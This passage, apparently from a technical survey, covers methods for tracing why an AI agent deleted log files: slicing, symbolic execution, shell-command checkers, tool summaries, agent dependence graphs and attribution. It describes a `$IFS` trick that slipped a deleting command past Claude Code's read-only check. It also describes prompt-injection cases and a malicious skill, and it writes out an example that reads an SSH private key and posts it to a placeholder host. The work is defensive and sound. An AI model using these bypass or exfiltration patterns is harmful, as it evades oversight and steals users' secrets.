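4. The sine of 2 is about 0.909 and the cosine about −0.416. Their product is negative, and a run of the original program confirms that it takes the branch.

The same method could help with a script that reads each log's age from a date in its file name. The solver would find that the age must be above 30, and the helper code would turn an age of 31 back into a file name. Gordian's coverage was 28.5% to 115.2% higher than that of the best traditional engine, depending on the set of programs. Its gain was even larger over engines that rely mainly on a model, and it used over 90% fewer tokens than they did.

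Symbolon, by Zhu and colleagues, has an agent rewrite the program. In the image-file example, the number of passes through a loop depends on a 16-bit number in the file, so the engine might have to consider tens of thousands of possibilities. A 300-byte file has room for only 23 entries, so the agent fixed the loop at 23 passes. It also removed a print statement and assumed one of the two valid codes. KLEE then analysed the simpler program, and Symbolon ran the resulting inputs on the original. Across 32 programs, this increased line coverage to 3.69 times what KLEE achieved alone. The inputs are reliable because the original program ran on them, but KLEE never explored the paths that the rewriting removed. If an engine finds no deletion in a rewritten script, the original might therefore still be able to delete something.

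Granberry and colleagues combine all three kinds of evidence on the principle that "the LLM proposes, the solver checks, concrete execution confirms." Agents write the stubs and a specification of what each function should do, CrossHair searches for inputs that violate it, and another agent judges whether each violation is a real bug. The system then writes a test that has to reproduce the bug in the unmodified application. It reproduced 1,050 bugs this way, but CrossHair had found only 221 of them. The agents had noticed the other 829 while reading the code to write the specifications.

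When Granberry and colleagues had the same model inspect the code on its own, it found 1,824 bugs, which the same kind of test reproduced. That is a strong result for reading alone, but the model missed 312 of the bugs that the combined system found, including about a third of CrossHair's. CrossHair was best at finding crashes on unusual inputs, such as empty strings and missing fields. For an agent's script, it would make sense to have a model read the code first and then use an engine to look for strange tool returns that the model overlooked.

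CrossHair explored all the paths within its limits for only 3.6% of the functions, and Granberry and colleagues describe even this as strong evidence, not proof. Establishing that the README can never affect logs older than 30 days is easier, because the log program's four paths cover every case and the solver can check each one.

### Engines that rely on a model's judgement

AutoExe, by Li and colleagues, replaces the solver with a language model. It first groups a program's paths by the statements they visit. The log program has six groups, however many logs there are, because line 4 either runs or doesn't, and in each case the loop may find no logs, find logs but delete none, or delete at least one. For each group, AutoExe removes the code that those paths don't visit and slices away anything irrelevant to the claim it is testing. The model then judges from the remaining code whether the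 claim always holds. The number of groups is finite, so the analysis always finishes, even for a program with an endless loop.

Checking one case at a time helps because models make fewer mistakes on smaller pieces of code. In one example, GPT-4o mini had to judge the claim that a function for rounding to the nearest integer never returns a number larger in absolute value than its input. It accepted the claim when given the whole function, but correctly rejected it when given only the code for positive numbers ending in .5, since the function rounds 2.5 up to 3.

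On 85 short Python programs, the average accuracy of seven models was 91.1% with AutoExe and 86.4% when they read each program whole. On 31 harder programs in Python and C, the averages were 72.4% with AutoExe and 65.9% without it. The gain was largest for one of the smaller models, and another model did worse with AutoExe on both sets. All seven are old and fairly weak by current standards, so current models would probably score higher with or without AutoExe. Li and colleagues also tried CrossHair on the Python programs in the harder set, and it found no violations. For some programs, the only realistic options may therefore be an answer that could be wrong or no answer.

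If AutoExe's model decides that a claim is false and gives an example, running the program on that example will show whether the model is right. An answer that a claim is true can't be checked this way, so it is weaker evidence, but an investigator needs this kind of answer to rule out the README as a cause.

Having a second model check the first does not remove this problem. In *NEUROTESTGEN* (2026), one model suggests inputs for paths that depend on text operations or on whether two names refer to the same object. Another model traces the code without running it to see whether each input would lead to the intended path. If not, it returns the input with a reason. This may catch careless mistakes, but both models could misunderstand the same operation. Running the code is a better test when it is safe to do so.

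*Can Large Language Models Reason About Complex Execution Paths?* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2025) tested whether models could find an input that exactly reproduced each of 509 recorded paths through Python programs. The paths averaged 233 statements and 103 branches, far more than in a run of the log program on a few logs. Running the programs confirmed that the best models succeeded on more than 65% of the paths. Models could also tell possible paths from impossible ones to some extent, but long reasoning sometimes led them to the wrong conclusion.

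Models have done much worse at listing every path. Feng and colleagues trained GPT-4o on KLEE's output for 80 of their C programs and had it predict the output for the other 20. It gave the correct number of paths for four of those 20. For the 15-line program with 1,002 paths, it predicted 12. Newer models would probably do better, but even a much smaller error could leave out the one path on which the program deletes a file.

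## Tracing through shell commands, tools and model calls

Slicing and symbolic execution only work on code that an analyser can read. In the log program, dependences pass outside that code on lines 2, 5 and 9, where the program calls a tool. They would also do so if the agent had written shell commands, which rely on other programs for most of the work, or if the program had called a language model. At each of these points, the analysis needs dependence edges that can't be determined from the code alone. Omitting an edge can hide the cause of a deletion, while adding too many can make the cause hard to find among irrelevant dependences.

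### Shell commands

An agent could also clear out old logs with a few lines of shell:

```sh
1   days=30
2   if grep -q "retention: 7" README.md; then
3       days=7
4   fi
5   find /srv/app/logs -type f -mtime +$days -delete
```

`grep -q` checks whether a file contains some text, so line 3 has a control dependence on line 2 and, through it, on the README. Line 5 has a data dependence on `days`. Ordinary slicing can find both dependences. But a trace of the run would have a single entry for line 5, however many logs it deleted, because the loop and the age test are inside `find`, a compiled program. To explain why `worker.log` is gone, an investigator has to know that `-mtime +7` selects files more than seven whole days old and that `-delete` removes them.

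The shell also rewrites each command before running it, which is called expansion. It replaces variables with their values, splits the result into separate arguments, and replaces patterns such as `*.log` with the names of matching files. The final command can therefore depend on things that don't appear in its text. For example, the files that `rm *.log` deletes depend on every earlier command that created, renamed or removed a file in the current folder. If no command has set `dir`, then `rm -rf "$dir"/*` becomes `rm -rf /*`, which tries to delete everything on the machine. The missing value caused the damage, but a graph that links each use of a variable to the statement that set it has no edge for `dir`, because no statement set it.

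Expansion is easy to handle after a run if it was recorded, and bash has an option to print each command after expansion. Before a run, a sound analysis has to assume that `*.log` could match any name with that ending.

Shell scripts also pass data through files. Suppose the agent had split line 5 in two:

```sh
find /srv/app/logs -type f -mtime +$days > /tmp/old.txt
xargs rm < /tmp/old.txt
```

No variable connects these commands, so a slicer has to treat `/tmp/old.txt` as a variable that the first command sets and the second uses. It also has to recognise when two paths lead to the same file. This is the alias problem again, because a symbolic link can give any file a second name. The current folder is another hidden variable. If a script runs `cd /srv/app/logs` and then `rm *.log`, and the `cd` fails, the shell normally carries on and deletes the `.log` files in whatever folder it was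 in before. When an agent keeps one shell session open, the `cd` may have run several steps before the `rm`.

### What command checkers establish

Much of the recent work on agents' shell commands aims to stop bad ones before they run. *Look Before You Leap* (Althoubi, 2026) tests a checker that has bash parse a command without running it, looks for the program on the machine, and compares each option with those in the program's help text. The test used 9,930 commands for 482 installed programs. Of the commands, 1,986 were valid and came from a human-written collection. The rest each contained a deliberate error: a nonexistent program, broken syntax, or an option that the program doesn't accept.

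The checker caught 95.8% of the invalid commands and wrongly flagged 10.0% of the valid ones. All the false alarms came from the option check, because the checker had failed to extract some real options from the help text. The other two checks raised no false alarms but caught only half of the errors. When the checker skipped options with one dash and several letters, which are the most ambiguous, false alarms fell to 7.0% and it caught just as many errors. This result makes the method look slightly better than it is, because none of the deliberate errors involved an option of this type.

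The `-type`, `-mtime` and `-delete` options in the `find` command above are all of this kind, so the second version would not check them. They are valid, but the command would be equally valid with a limit of 7 days or 30, or with the wrong folder. Althoubi says that the checker judges only whether a command can run as written, not whether the change is the right one.

In *CARE*, Liu, Zhang and colleagues (2026) describe a checker that looks for harmful commands instead of invalid ones. They cite a flaw in Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code that let commands get past a check for read-only commands. One trick used the variable `$IFS`, which normally holds a space, a tab and a line break. Once the shell expands the variable, `rm$IFS/srv/app/logs/worker.log` deletes the log, but a checker that splits commands at spaces would find only one word.

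CARE first removes such disguises as far as it can without running anything. It unwraps commands inside other commands, normalises quotation marks and decodes simple encodings. It then parses the command and scores it on its structure, its type, the paths it touches and any match with known dangerous patterns. CARE allows commands with low scores, blocks those with high scores, and uses a language model to decide most of the cases in between. On the main test, it had an F1 score of 85.64%, which combines the share of harmful commands it caught with the share of its alarms that were correct. It flagged 0.91% of harmless commands and took 2.32 milliseconds on average. Without the language model, F1 was 84.99%, so the fixed rules account for nearly all of the score.

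CARE's path analysis would be useful for tracing because it expands home folders, follows symbolic links and separates reading from writing. This is roughly what a slicer needs to treat a command as a statement that uses some files and sets others. But CARE classifies a command as reading or writing by its name, which isn't enough for `find`, since it only reads unless it has an option such as `-delete`. CARE also checks each command separately, so it wouldn't connect `xargs rm < /tmp/old.txt` to the command that chose the files.

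A valid command that passes every check can still have an effect that its text doesn't reveal. Althoubi also tested 640 edits to 224 Python files. Edits that specified their target by line number corrupted 99.1% of files without an error when the file had shifted by one line. Edits that specified their target by quoting the surrounding code exactly failed visibly if they found no match. So if an agent had edited `cleanup.py` by line number, the edit command would be poor evidence of what the script contained when it ran.

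### Effect summaries for tools

When an analyser can't read a tool's code, it can use an effect summary, which lists what the tool reads, what it changes and what its result depends on. The log program needs three:

| Tool | Reads | Changes | Result depends on |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_file(path)` | The file at `path` | Nothing | The path and the file's contents |
| `list_files(folder)` | Names, sizes and ages of the files in `folder` | Nothing | The folder's contents and the current time |
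| `delete(path)` | Whether the file exists | The file at `path`, and so its folder | The path and whether the file exists |

With these summaries, a slicer can follow dependences through the file system. If the program listed the logs again after the loop, the second list would depend on every deletion. *AgentArmor* keeps similar summaries in a registry. Its example is `git_clone`, which copies a code repository. The record of the call contains only the repository's address, but the registry adds that the tool creates a local folder whose contents come from that address. If a later step runs a script from the folder, the graph has a path from that step back to the address.

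An error in a summary leads to an error in the trace. Suppose `list_files` leaves out any log named in a hidden `.keep` file, and its summary doesn't mention this. Somebody asking why a 45-day-old log survived would trace the list to line 5 and not find out about the `.keep` file. If `list_files` also reset the age of every log it examined, the next cleanup would spare logs it should have deleted, and a trace based on a summary that omitted the reset wouldn't connect this to the earlier call. Extra entries in a summary are safer but make slices larger. If the summary for `delete` listed the whole folder as changed, each deletion would appear to depend on all the earlier ones.

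If a tool has no summary, a sound analysis has to assume that the tool could change anything, as it does with `exec`, so it treats every later tool result as depending on that tool. Assuming that an unknown tool changes nothing gives short slices, but they could miss the cause.

The easiest source for a tool's summary is the description its developer writes so that the model knows when to use it, but nothing ensures that this description matches the code. *ACaM* (Santra, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) cites research that found mismatches in 10% to 13% of cases. It also gives an example of two tools that together leak an access token, though neither looks suspicious on its own. One fetches news and stores its access token in a shared dictionary. The other sends the whole dictionary to a server to synchronise the user's preferences. Neither tool's description mentions the leak.

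The ACaM system analyzes each tool's source code to work out what the tool can do. Fixed rules identify most of the channels through which data enters or leaves a function, such as files, network calls and shared variables, and a language model adds channels that the rules miss. The model can mark data as more sensitive than the rules did, but never less. If the analysis can't resolve some piece of code, it marks the code as unknown rather than treating it as safe.

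ACaM identified the tools' capabilities in 24 hand-annotated agents with an average F1 score of 98.3%. Santra and colleagues also planted chains of vulnerable tools in the agents. ACaM scored 0.980 for reconstructing these chains, against 0.903 for the best method using only a language model and at most 0.342 for methods using only static analysis. Planted chains may be easier to find than natural ones, but ACaM also found 123 paths to code execution or exposed credentials in 43 unmodified agents, and the researchers confirmed these paths by hand in the code. The method needs source code, so it can't help with tools that run on somebody else's server. For those, the investigator has only the tools' descriptions and recorded results.

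### Model calls inside the program

A program can also call a language model as it runs. In this variant of the log program, a model reads the README and returns the number of days:

```python
1   request = "Delete logs older than 30 days."
2   notes = read_file("README.md")
3   answer = ask_model("How long should we keep logs, in days?", request, notes)
4   days = int(answer)
```

Lines 5 to 11 are unchanged. Suppose the README has 200 lines, and one of them is "Keep logs for one week." The exact-phrase test would have missed this sentence, but the model returns "7", and the program deletes `worker.log`.

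A slicer has no rules for what happens inside line 3, so the safe choice is to assume that every input affects every output. The dynamic slice of the deletion is lines 1 to 5 and 7 to 9, which includes all 200 lines of the README and the user's 30 days. In the original program, a dynamic slicer could drop the 30 because line 4 visibly replaced it. Here the 30 may have had no effect on the model's output, or it may have influenced the output along with the README, and the trace doesn't show which.

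This loss of precision is tolerable with one model call, but it compounds when calls feed into each other. Suppose the program sent each log to the model separately and included the model's previous answers for consistency. Each deletion would then depend on every earlier answer and on all the logs used to produce them, so after a few passes the slice would contain nearly everything that had happened.

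Some programs make many model calls. *Recursive Language Models* (Zhang, Kraska and Khattab, 2025) stores a long prompt as a variable in a Python session. The main model receives only basic facts about the text, such as its length and first few words. It then writes code that splits the text into pieces and calls a model on them, often in a loop. On questions that required comparing pairs of entries in a 32,000-token text, GPT-5 had an F1 score of 0.1% alone and 58.0% with this method.

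Several small model calls are easier to trace than one large call. If a program cuts the README into ten pieces and asks about each separately, the answer about the third piece can't depend on the seventh. A slicer can then assume that each answer depends on everything in its call's input without adding many false dependencies. The benefit disappears if a final model call receives all ten answers, but if ordinary code combines them, for example by taking the smallest number, the slicer can identify the call that returned that number.

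The safe assumption must also cover everything the called model can do, so if the model has its own tools, the summary of line 3 must include all their possible effects. *Agent-Native by Design* (Dantanarayana, Kashmira and colleagues, 2026) describes Jac, an extension of Python in which a model call declares its inputs, the type of its result and the tools it may use. The compiler uses these declarations to check dependences before it starts a likely next step early, but they would also help an investigator. For example, a call that must return a whole number can't pass a sentence from the README to the rest of the program through its result.

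Drawing edges only from the inputs that seem to have affected the model's output gives a much shorter slice. Attribution methods can estimate which inputs these were. An estimate might include the sentence about one week and exclude both the 30 days and the other 199 lines. But these estimates can be wrong. For example, the README might also say that logs keep filling the disk, and that sentence may have led the model to choose the shorter period. If the estimate missed that sentence, the slice would omit it too.

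It seems best to keep all the safe edges and attach the estimates to them as weights. An investigator can then start with the most likely causes without using an estimate to rule any out. When the model also chooses which tools to call, edges from inputs to outputs are not enough, and each choice needs a control dependence as well. Santra and colleagues object to analysers that treat a model as a box through which data simply passes, because this breaks legitimate flows and misses real problems.

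Symbolic execution can narrow the question about line 3 by treating the model's answer as an unknown number *d*. The program deletes the 12-day-old `worker.log` exactly when *d* is below 12, so the investigator only has to explain why the model chose a number below 12, not why it chose 7 in particular. The answer's format also matters. If the model had returned "7 days", `int` would have raised an error and the program would have stopped before deleting anything.

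### Slicing over the steps of an agent

An agent makes a model call between any two steps, and the input to that call is the whole context. If every part of the input affects every output, each step depends on all the earlier ones, and a backward slice from the deletion contains the entire session up to that point. A method needs another source of dependence edges to produce a shorter slice.

*AgentArmor* has a language model infer them from the record of the run:

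1. It turns the run into a chain of prompts, thoughts, tool calls and results, and splits each call into the tool's name and its parameters.
2. It adds files and other data that the tools' summaries mention but the record doesn't.
3. For each call, it gives a language model the earlier prompts and results, along with the agent's stated reasoning. The model lists the ones that contributed to the call and explains why.

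If the agent had deleted the logs with direct tool calls, the model would probably add a control edge from the request U to the choice of `delete` and a data edge from the list of files to the path. In the code action, the entire program is one parameter, so the graph might link the wiki page W to the program, but not to the 7 on line 4.

*AgentArmor* uses the graph to stop attacks by marking some data as untrusted or confidential, passing these labels along the edges and blocking calls that break a rule. On AgentDojo, a set of simulated tasks with malicious instructions planted in the data, it reduced the attack success rate from 41% to 3%, while task completion fell only from 73% to 72%. CaMeL, a stricter system that tracks data through generated code by fixed rules, allowed no successful attacks but completed only 48% of tasks. The inferred edges in *AgentArmor* let the agent complete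 many more tasks, but they also let a few attacks through.

Some of those misses come from tasks in which the user asks the agent to follow a file's instructions. In one, the user tells the agent to read a landlord's notice and do exactly what it says, and the notice contains the attack. With GPT-4o, *AgentArmor* detected only 40% of the attacks in the category where such tasks were common. Building the graph also uses many tokens, 13,609 on average. The scores are only indirect evidence that the graph's edges are correct, because they measure whether the system blocked the right calls, and a graph with some wrong edges can still lead to the right decision.

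*FALAT* (Rafi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) diagnoses failed runs by using a language model to label whether later steps build on a suspicious step, repeat it, correct it, ignore it or introduce a new error. The system uses these labels to search for the step whose correction would have led to the right result. It found the step that the benchmark marked as decisive in 46.0% of algorithm-generated runs and 29.1% of harder, hand-crafted ones. These were the best results among the methods tested, and newer models would probably do better, but it would still be unwise to base an explanation on inferred steps alone.

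### Reading the agent's own source code

Edges can also come from the program that sets up the agent's model, prompts and tools. *AGENTFLOW* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026) analyses agents written with five popular frameworks, including LangGraph and the OpenAI Agents SDK. An ordinary analyser treats a line like `Agent(tools=[send_email])` as a function call with a list argument. AgentFlow has rules for 143 constructs of this kind, and from this one it infers that the agent may call `send_email` and that text in the agent's prompt may influence what the agent sends.

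The resulting graph has nodes for agents, prompts, models, tools, memory and approval rules. Its edges show which components belong together, where control can pass and where data can flow. Like a static slice, it covers everything that could happen in some run. In the log example, it could show in advance that a wiki page may influence code that deletes files, but not that W did so in the recorded session.

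Wang and colleagues searched 5,399 agent projects for paths by which text from a prompt could reach the arguments of a sensitive tool. They found 4,357 such paths in 238 projects (4.4% of the projects searched). The tools at the end of these paths most often sent data elsewhere (129 projects) or accessed files (74). They checked 100 of the reported paths by hand, and 73 were real vulnerabilities. In 25 of the other 27, the path existed but the tool was fairly harmless, such as one that could only read from a database. The dependence was therefore real in 98 of the 100 cases, which is encouraging for tracing.

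The number of risks AgentFlow misses is harder to estimate. The researchers also inspected 100 agents that had powerful tools but for which AgentFlow had reported no risks, and found overlooked risks in nine. The main causes were custom wrappers around commands, and tools that the agent connects only as it runs. Most projects had no reports, so if many of them contain agents like these, the missed risks could outnumber the ones AgentFlow found. AgentFlow also doesn't cover finished products such as Claude Code, and it doesn't analyse the code inside each tool.

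*From Noisy Traces to Root Causes* (Chang, Xu and colleagues, 2026) presents STRACE, a system for improving agents by learning from their failures. A language model reads the agent's source code and builds a graph of the data and control dependences between its modules, such as its planner and its code runner. STRACE then takes the record of a failed run, starts at the step where the error appeared and follows these dependences backwards, discarding any step that has no path to the error. A model reads the remaining steps, decides which module was at fault and adds advice to that module's prompt.

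On VeruSAGE-Bench, a set of tasks that involve proving Rust programs correct, this raised an agent's success rate from 42.5% to 58.5%. In one group of 25 failures, STRACE blamed an earlier module than the one where the error appeared in 12 cases. It's tempting to credit the slicing for the improvement, but the tests of each component don't support that:

| Version of STRACE | Success rate | Cost of optimisation |
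|---|---|---|
| Complete | 56% | $2.96 |
| No slicing, only the step where the error appeared | 54% | $2.88 |
| No slicing, the whole run | 54% | $5.93 |
| No dependence graph | 48% | $5.10 |

Slicing added two percentage points to the success rate, which would be one task in a test of 50. Its clearer benefit was halving the cost compared with reading the whole run. The graph seems to matter more, though perhaps not because its edges are exactly right. Removing a quarter of them at random reduced the success rate only to 54%, and adding 10% more edges at random raised it to 62%. Random edges should not help, so differences of a few points are probably noise.

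An approximate graph may be good enough for improving prompts, because bad advice shows up in later results, but an error in the explanation of one deletion would not be caught this way. The dependences in STRACE are also between modules rather than individual steps, so if the planner can influence the code runner, the slice may keep an earlier planning step that had nothing to do with the logs.

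### Using only recorded links

Ying, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *AgentTriage*, take the opposite approach and do not let a language model infer anything. Their system connects two events only if the record contains evidence of the link:

- the agent's software named one event as the parent of the other;
- both events have the same call number, as a request and its result do;
- the software recorded that a value from one event went into a particular argument of the other.

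AgentTriage doesn't add an edge between two events just because they are close together in time or contain the same text. In one test, a user asked an agent to write to `/sg01.txt`, and the agent called a file-writing tool with that path. AgentTriage connected the request to the call because the software had recorded each event's parent along the way. But it listed the origin of the path as unverified, since nothing recorded where the argument came from. A person would have little doubt that the path came from the request, but the strict rule matters more for a value like 7, which could have come from many places.

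AgentTriage also distinguishes attempted effects from completed ones. A request to delete `worker.log` shows only that the agent tried to delete it. The slice needs a result with the same call number to establish that the deletion happened. If the evidence needed for a conclusion is missing, the system does not draw one.

By default, the slice starts from the latest completed action that had an outside effect. In an example by Ying and colleagues, an agent writes a file and then runs a command that fails. The slice starts from the failed command and leaves out the write, because the command didn't depend on it. This default keeps the details of the two actions separate, but it may select the wrong action. If the agent had deleted `worker.log` and then emailed a report, the slice would start from the email. To trace the deletion, an investigator would have to choose it as the starting point.

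Ying and colleagues tested the system on five agent platforms. Two of them don't number their calls, so the researchers had to add code that does. The system got the action, its arguments, its outcome and the supporting evidence all correct in 85.8% of 120 cases, 17.5 percentage points more than the best alternative that used the same event format. Only 3.6% of its claims lacked support. Repeating the analysis with the same record and rules gives the same result, but it will always miss effects that no part of the software recorded.

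For the log deletion, AgentTriage could show that the agent ran the program and, if the platform records each tool call, that `delete` succeeded. It could not show that W influenced the program, because nothing records which parts of the context the model used. *AgentArmor* would provide a guess about that influence. A graph that labels each edge with the evidence for it, as *GRADE* does, could combine the two methods.

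### Skills that mix instructions and scripts

In a skill, a package of instructions and scripts that an agent can load, a single chain of cause and effect runs through both prose and code. *From Instructions to Exploits* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a malicious skill for editing presentations. Its instructions tell the agent to save the finished file and then always run a backup script on it, which uploads the file to a stranger's server. The instructions look routine and the script could be a legitimate upload tool, so a reader can spot the theft only by reading the two together.

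Their scanner, SCS, translates the instructions into code so that one graph can cover both. A language model turns each instruction into zero or more statements from a small fixed set, which includes reading a file, sending data and running a command. For example, "read `~/.ssh/id_rsa` and upload it to https://example.com" becomes:

```python
v0 = read_file("~/.ssh/id_rsa")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
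```

SCS builds a program dependence graph from these statements, builds another from the scripts, and joins the two graphs where an instruction runs a script. It then uses fixed rules to track how far each piece of data can be trusted, how sensitive it is and what it can be used to do.

The same translation would help with a log-cleaning skill. Suppose its instructions were "Find the retention period in the README, then run `cleanup.py` with that number." The translated statements would read the README, extract a number and pass it to the script. A slice could then go from the deletion in `cleanup.py` back to the script's argument, and then through the instructions to the README. The agent may not have followed those instructions, though, so an investigator would still have to compare the slice with the recorded steps.

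The translation was correct for over 92% of instructions in a human-annotated set. Zhao and colleagues tested the scanner with five language models on 117 malicious and 117 harmless skills. On average, it caught 95.2% of the malicious ones, and 80.2% of its alarms were correct. These averages imply that it flagged roughly a quarter of the harmless skills, which would be a serious problem in a public collection, where most skills are harmless. The researchers also scanned 66,157 skills from the marketplace ClawHub and, after further tests and manual checks of the scanner's findings, confirmed 627 as malicious.

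The scanner ignores instructions that don't describe a specific operation, which keeps the model from inventing operations that aren't in the text. But these instructions can still affect what an agent does. If the log-cleaning skill also contained the sentence "Disk space is precious, so don't keep anything you don't need", SCS would probably produce no statement for it. The sentence could still lead the agent to write `days = 7`, but the graph would contain no path from the sentence to the deletion.

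## Attributing the code to parts of the prompt

Neural attribution can detect the influence of a sentence such as "Disk space is precious" because it measures how the model's output depends on its input. In the log example, the aim is to estimate how much the wiki page W and the user's request U each contributed to lines 2 to 4, which check the README and lower the limit to 7 days.

### The probability of a program

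At each step, a language model assigns a probability to every token in its vocabulary, and the software running the model picks one. The probability of a whole program is the product of the probabilities of its tokens, and taking logarithms turns this product into a sum. For a prompt X and a program Y with tokens y₁ to yₙ,

log p(Y | X) = log p(y₁ | X) + log p(y₂ | X, y₁) + … + log p(yₙ | X, y₁, …, yₙ₋₁).

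Each term depends on the prompt and on every token written so far. To measure the influence of one segment of the prompt, an investigator can remove it and score the same program again:

drop(s) = log p(Y | X) − log p(Y | X without s).

The model only computes the probability of tokens it has already written, which takes one forward pass (a single run of the network over the text). Suppose lines 2 to 4 have a probability of 0.2 with W in the prompt and 0.001 without it. W then makes those lines 200 times as likely, and the drop in log probability from removing it is the natural logarithm of 200, or about 5.3.

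Since the sum has a term for each token, the investigator can also see where in the program the drop occurs. It would be largest where the model started to read the README instead of listing the files. It would probably be close to zero at the 7 on line 4, which set the limit, because the model had already written "retention: 7" on line 3 and would very likely continue with `days = 7` with or without W. Scoring only the token that caused the damage could therefore miss the influence of W completely.

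Raw scores for single tokens are hard to read. *TokenScope* (Esmaeili, 2026) describes a tool that uses a parser to group token probabilities and other measurements by expression, statement, line or block. The tool also lets a user replace any token and have the model continue from there. An investigator could replace `notes` with `files` at the start of line 2 and see whether the code the model then writes still checks the README.

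### Removing segments

The simplest method removes one segment of the prompt at a time. With ten segments, it takes 11 forward passes, including one for the full prompt. This works well only if each segment affects the code independently of the others.

A more thorough method removes random sets of segments and fits a simple model to the results. In the version that Cohen-Wang, Chuang and Madry (2025), in *Learning to Attribute with Attention*, describe, each segment has a 50% chance of removal in each trial. Let vᵢ be 1 if segment i stays in and 0 if it doesn't. The method looks for weights w₁ to wₖ such that

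w₁v₁ + w₂v₂ + … + wₖvₖ

tracks the probability of the original output as closely as possible across the trials. The weight of each segment is its attribution score. This simple model, or surrogate, is valid for only one prompt and one output, so every new program needs a new set of trials. Cohen-Wang and colleagues used between 32 and 256.

An attribution is faithful if its scores match what the model actually relied on. Cohen-Wang and colleagues measure this in two ways. The first removes the five highest-scoring segments and records how far the log-probability of the output falls. The fall should be larger for a better method. The second removes many random sets of segments, predicts the effect of each removal by adding up scores, and calculates the rank correlation between predicted and actual effects. Both tests define influence as the effect of removal, which suits an investigator who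 wants to know what would have happened without W. But this also means neither test can reveal a problem with removal itself.

### Shapley values

Shapley values come from game theory, where they divide the winnings of a team among its members. Here the team members are segments of the prompt. The value of a segment i is

φᵢ = Σ over sets S without i of [|S|! (n − |S| − 1)! / n!] × [v(S ∪ {i}) − v(S)],

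where n is the number of segments and v(S) measures how well the model does with only the segments in S. The second bracket is the difference that segment i makes when it joins S. The first is a weight that makes the result an average over every order in which the segments could join.

*Toward Explaining Large Language Models in Software Engineering Tasks* (Vitale, Nguyen-Nguyen and colleagues, 2025) uses this formula in a tool called FeatureSHAP. A language model first splits the prompt into meaningful pieces, such as a task description or a constraint. FeatureSHAP then removes various combinations of pieces, has the model write a new program each time, and compares that program with the original. For code, v is CodeBLEU, a similarity score based on wording, syntax and data flow. The method needs only the text of each output, so it works on models whose probabilities aren't available.

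Each subset of the prompt's segments requires a complete new program, and n segments have 2ⁿ subsets, so 8 segments require 256 programs and 12 require 4,096. FeatureSHAP can sample the subsets instead of trying them all, which makes the scores approximate.

Vitale and colleagues tested FeatureSHAP by adding an irrelevant sentence to programming prompts, such as one about zebras finding their way through caves. They kept only the cases where the sentence left the model's output unchanged, so its correct score was close to zero. On code generation, FeatureSHAP gave these sentences an average score of 0.010 to 0.029, depending on the model. Random scores averaged 0.161 to 0.180.

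A harder version of the test used a sentence from another programming task. FeatureSHAP gave that sentence average scores of 0.009 to 0.025. GPT-5 mini, which read the prompt and the output and guessed the scores, averaged 0.014 to 0.028. Guessing did almost as well, so the test is probably too easy. Vitale and colleagues call a low score for irrelevant text necessary but not sufficient. An investigator mostly needs to compare passages that could all have mattered, such as U and W, which this test doesn't cover.

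Whole-program similarity would also be a poor measure for the log deletion. If the model wrote the same program without lines 2 to 4, `worker.log` would survive, but eight of the 11 lines would be identical, so the similarity would be high and W would get a low score. FeatureSHAP lets users choose a different comparison, and a better one here would be whether the new program lowers the limit when it finds the phrase in the README.

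### Attention weights and gradients

Removal and Shapley values both require many runs for each program. Attention, the mechanism by which a language model draws on earlier tokens when it produces the next one, provides evidence with less computation. Each of the network's many layers has several attention heads, and each head assigns a weight to every earlier token. These weights are available from the original run if someone saved them.

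Simply averaging them is unreliable, because heads do different jobs. In one example from Cohen-Wang and colleagues, a model had to find a player's shortest field goal in a report on an American football game. One head in layer 19 focused on the three distances that the answer mentioned, while two other heads focused on apparently unrelated words. Their method, AT2, learns how much to trust each head. The score of a segment s is

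score(s) = Σ over layers l and heads h of θₗₕ × Aₗₕ(s),

where Aₗₕ(s) is the attention that the head pays to the tokens of s, averaged over the tokens of the output, and θₗₕ is the learned weight of that head. To find these weights, Cohen-Wang and colleagues ran 32 random removals on each of 2,000 examples, which costs about 64,000 forward passes. After that, scoring a new output takes less than half as long as one forward pass. Compared with a surrogate that needs 32 passes each time, AT2 pays for its training after about 2,000 programs.

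In both of the researchers' tests, AT2 did about as well as surrogate models fitted to the results of many removals, and consistently better than averaged attention. It worked almost as well when its training examples came from a general collection rather than from the task itself. The researchers also used it to discard the less relevant passages before a model answered a question, which improved the answers. But the tests covered only question answering and summaries, on models with at most about 8 billion parameters. Attribution could be harder for code, because one short phrase in a long prompt may determine a line of code.

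Gradients are another way to avoid repeated removals. The network represents each token as a list of numbers, and a gradient shows how much the log-probability of the output would change if those numbers changed slightly:

gᵢ = ∂ log p(Y | X) / ∂xᵢ.

A common score for a segment is the sum of the absolute values of its tokens' gradients. Computing it requires access to the model's weights and takes one forward pass and one backward pass through the network, which took about eight times as long as AT2. AT2 also consistently beat this method. One likely reason is that a gradient measures the effect of a tiny change to a token, which can be very different from the effect of removing a whole page.

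### Graphs of internal features

An attribution graph goes further and traces the steps inside the network. He, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *CodeCircuit*, build one for each line of generated code. They replace part of every layer with a transcoder, a separately trained component that breaks the layer's activity into features, some of which people can interpret. The nodes of the graph are the tokens of the input, the active features and the possible outputs. The weight of an edge from node i to node j is

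wᵢⱼ = aᵢ × (vᵢₙ,ⱼᵀ Jᵢⱼ vₒᵤₜ,ᵢ),

where aᵢ is how active node i is, vₒᵤₜ,ᵢ is the direction in which it writes to the network's internal state, vᵢₙ,ⱼ is the direction from which node j reads, and Jᵢⱼ describes how the network carries the signal from one to the other. Extra error nodes stand for whatever the transcoders failed to reproduce. If much of the influence on a line comes from error nodes, the graph explains little.

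The method holds attention fixed at its values from the original run, so a graph could show that information moved from W to the README check, but not why the model attended to W.

CodeCircuit trains a classifier to predict whether a line of code is correct from properties of these graphs, such as their density and the share of influence from error nodes. The usual score for such a classifier is AUROC, the probability that it ranks a random wrong line as more likely to be wrong than a random correct one. Random guessing gives an AUROC of 50%.

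| Test | CodeCircuit | Best other method |
|---|---|---|
| Python | 79.9% | 51.4% |
| Java | 68.1% | 57.5% |
| C++ | 72.2% | 59.1% |

When He and colleagues trained the classifier on one language and tested it on another, the score fell to between 53% and 62%. Even within Python, catching 95% of the wrong lines would mean flagging 78% of the correct ones. The labels came from GPT-4o, which makes mistakes, and the study used a very small model, Gemma 2 2B.

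These scores show that the graphs contain some information about errors, but not that a graph identifies the part of the prompt that led to a line of code, which He and colleagues did not test. The closest evidence is a case study in which the model wrote `high = mid` in a binary search, a mistake that can cause an endless loop. The researchers used the graph to find one feature, and when they switched it off, the model wrote the correct `high = mid - 1`. This was a real intervention, but one success is not enough to estimate how often it would work.

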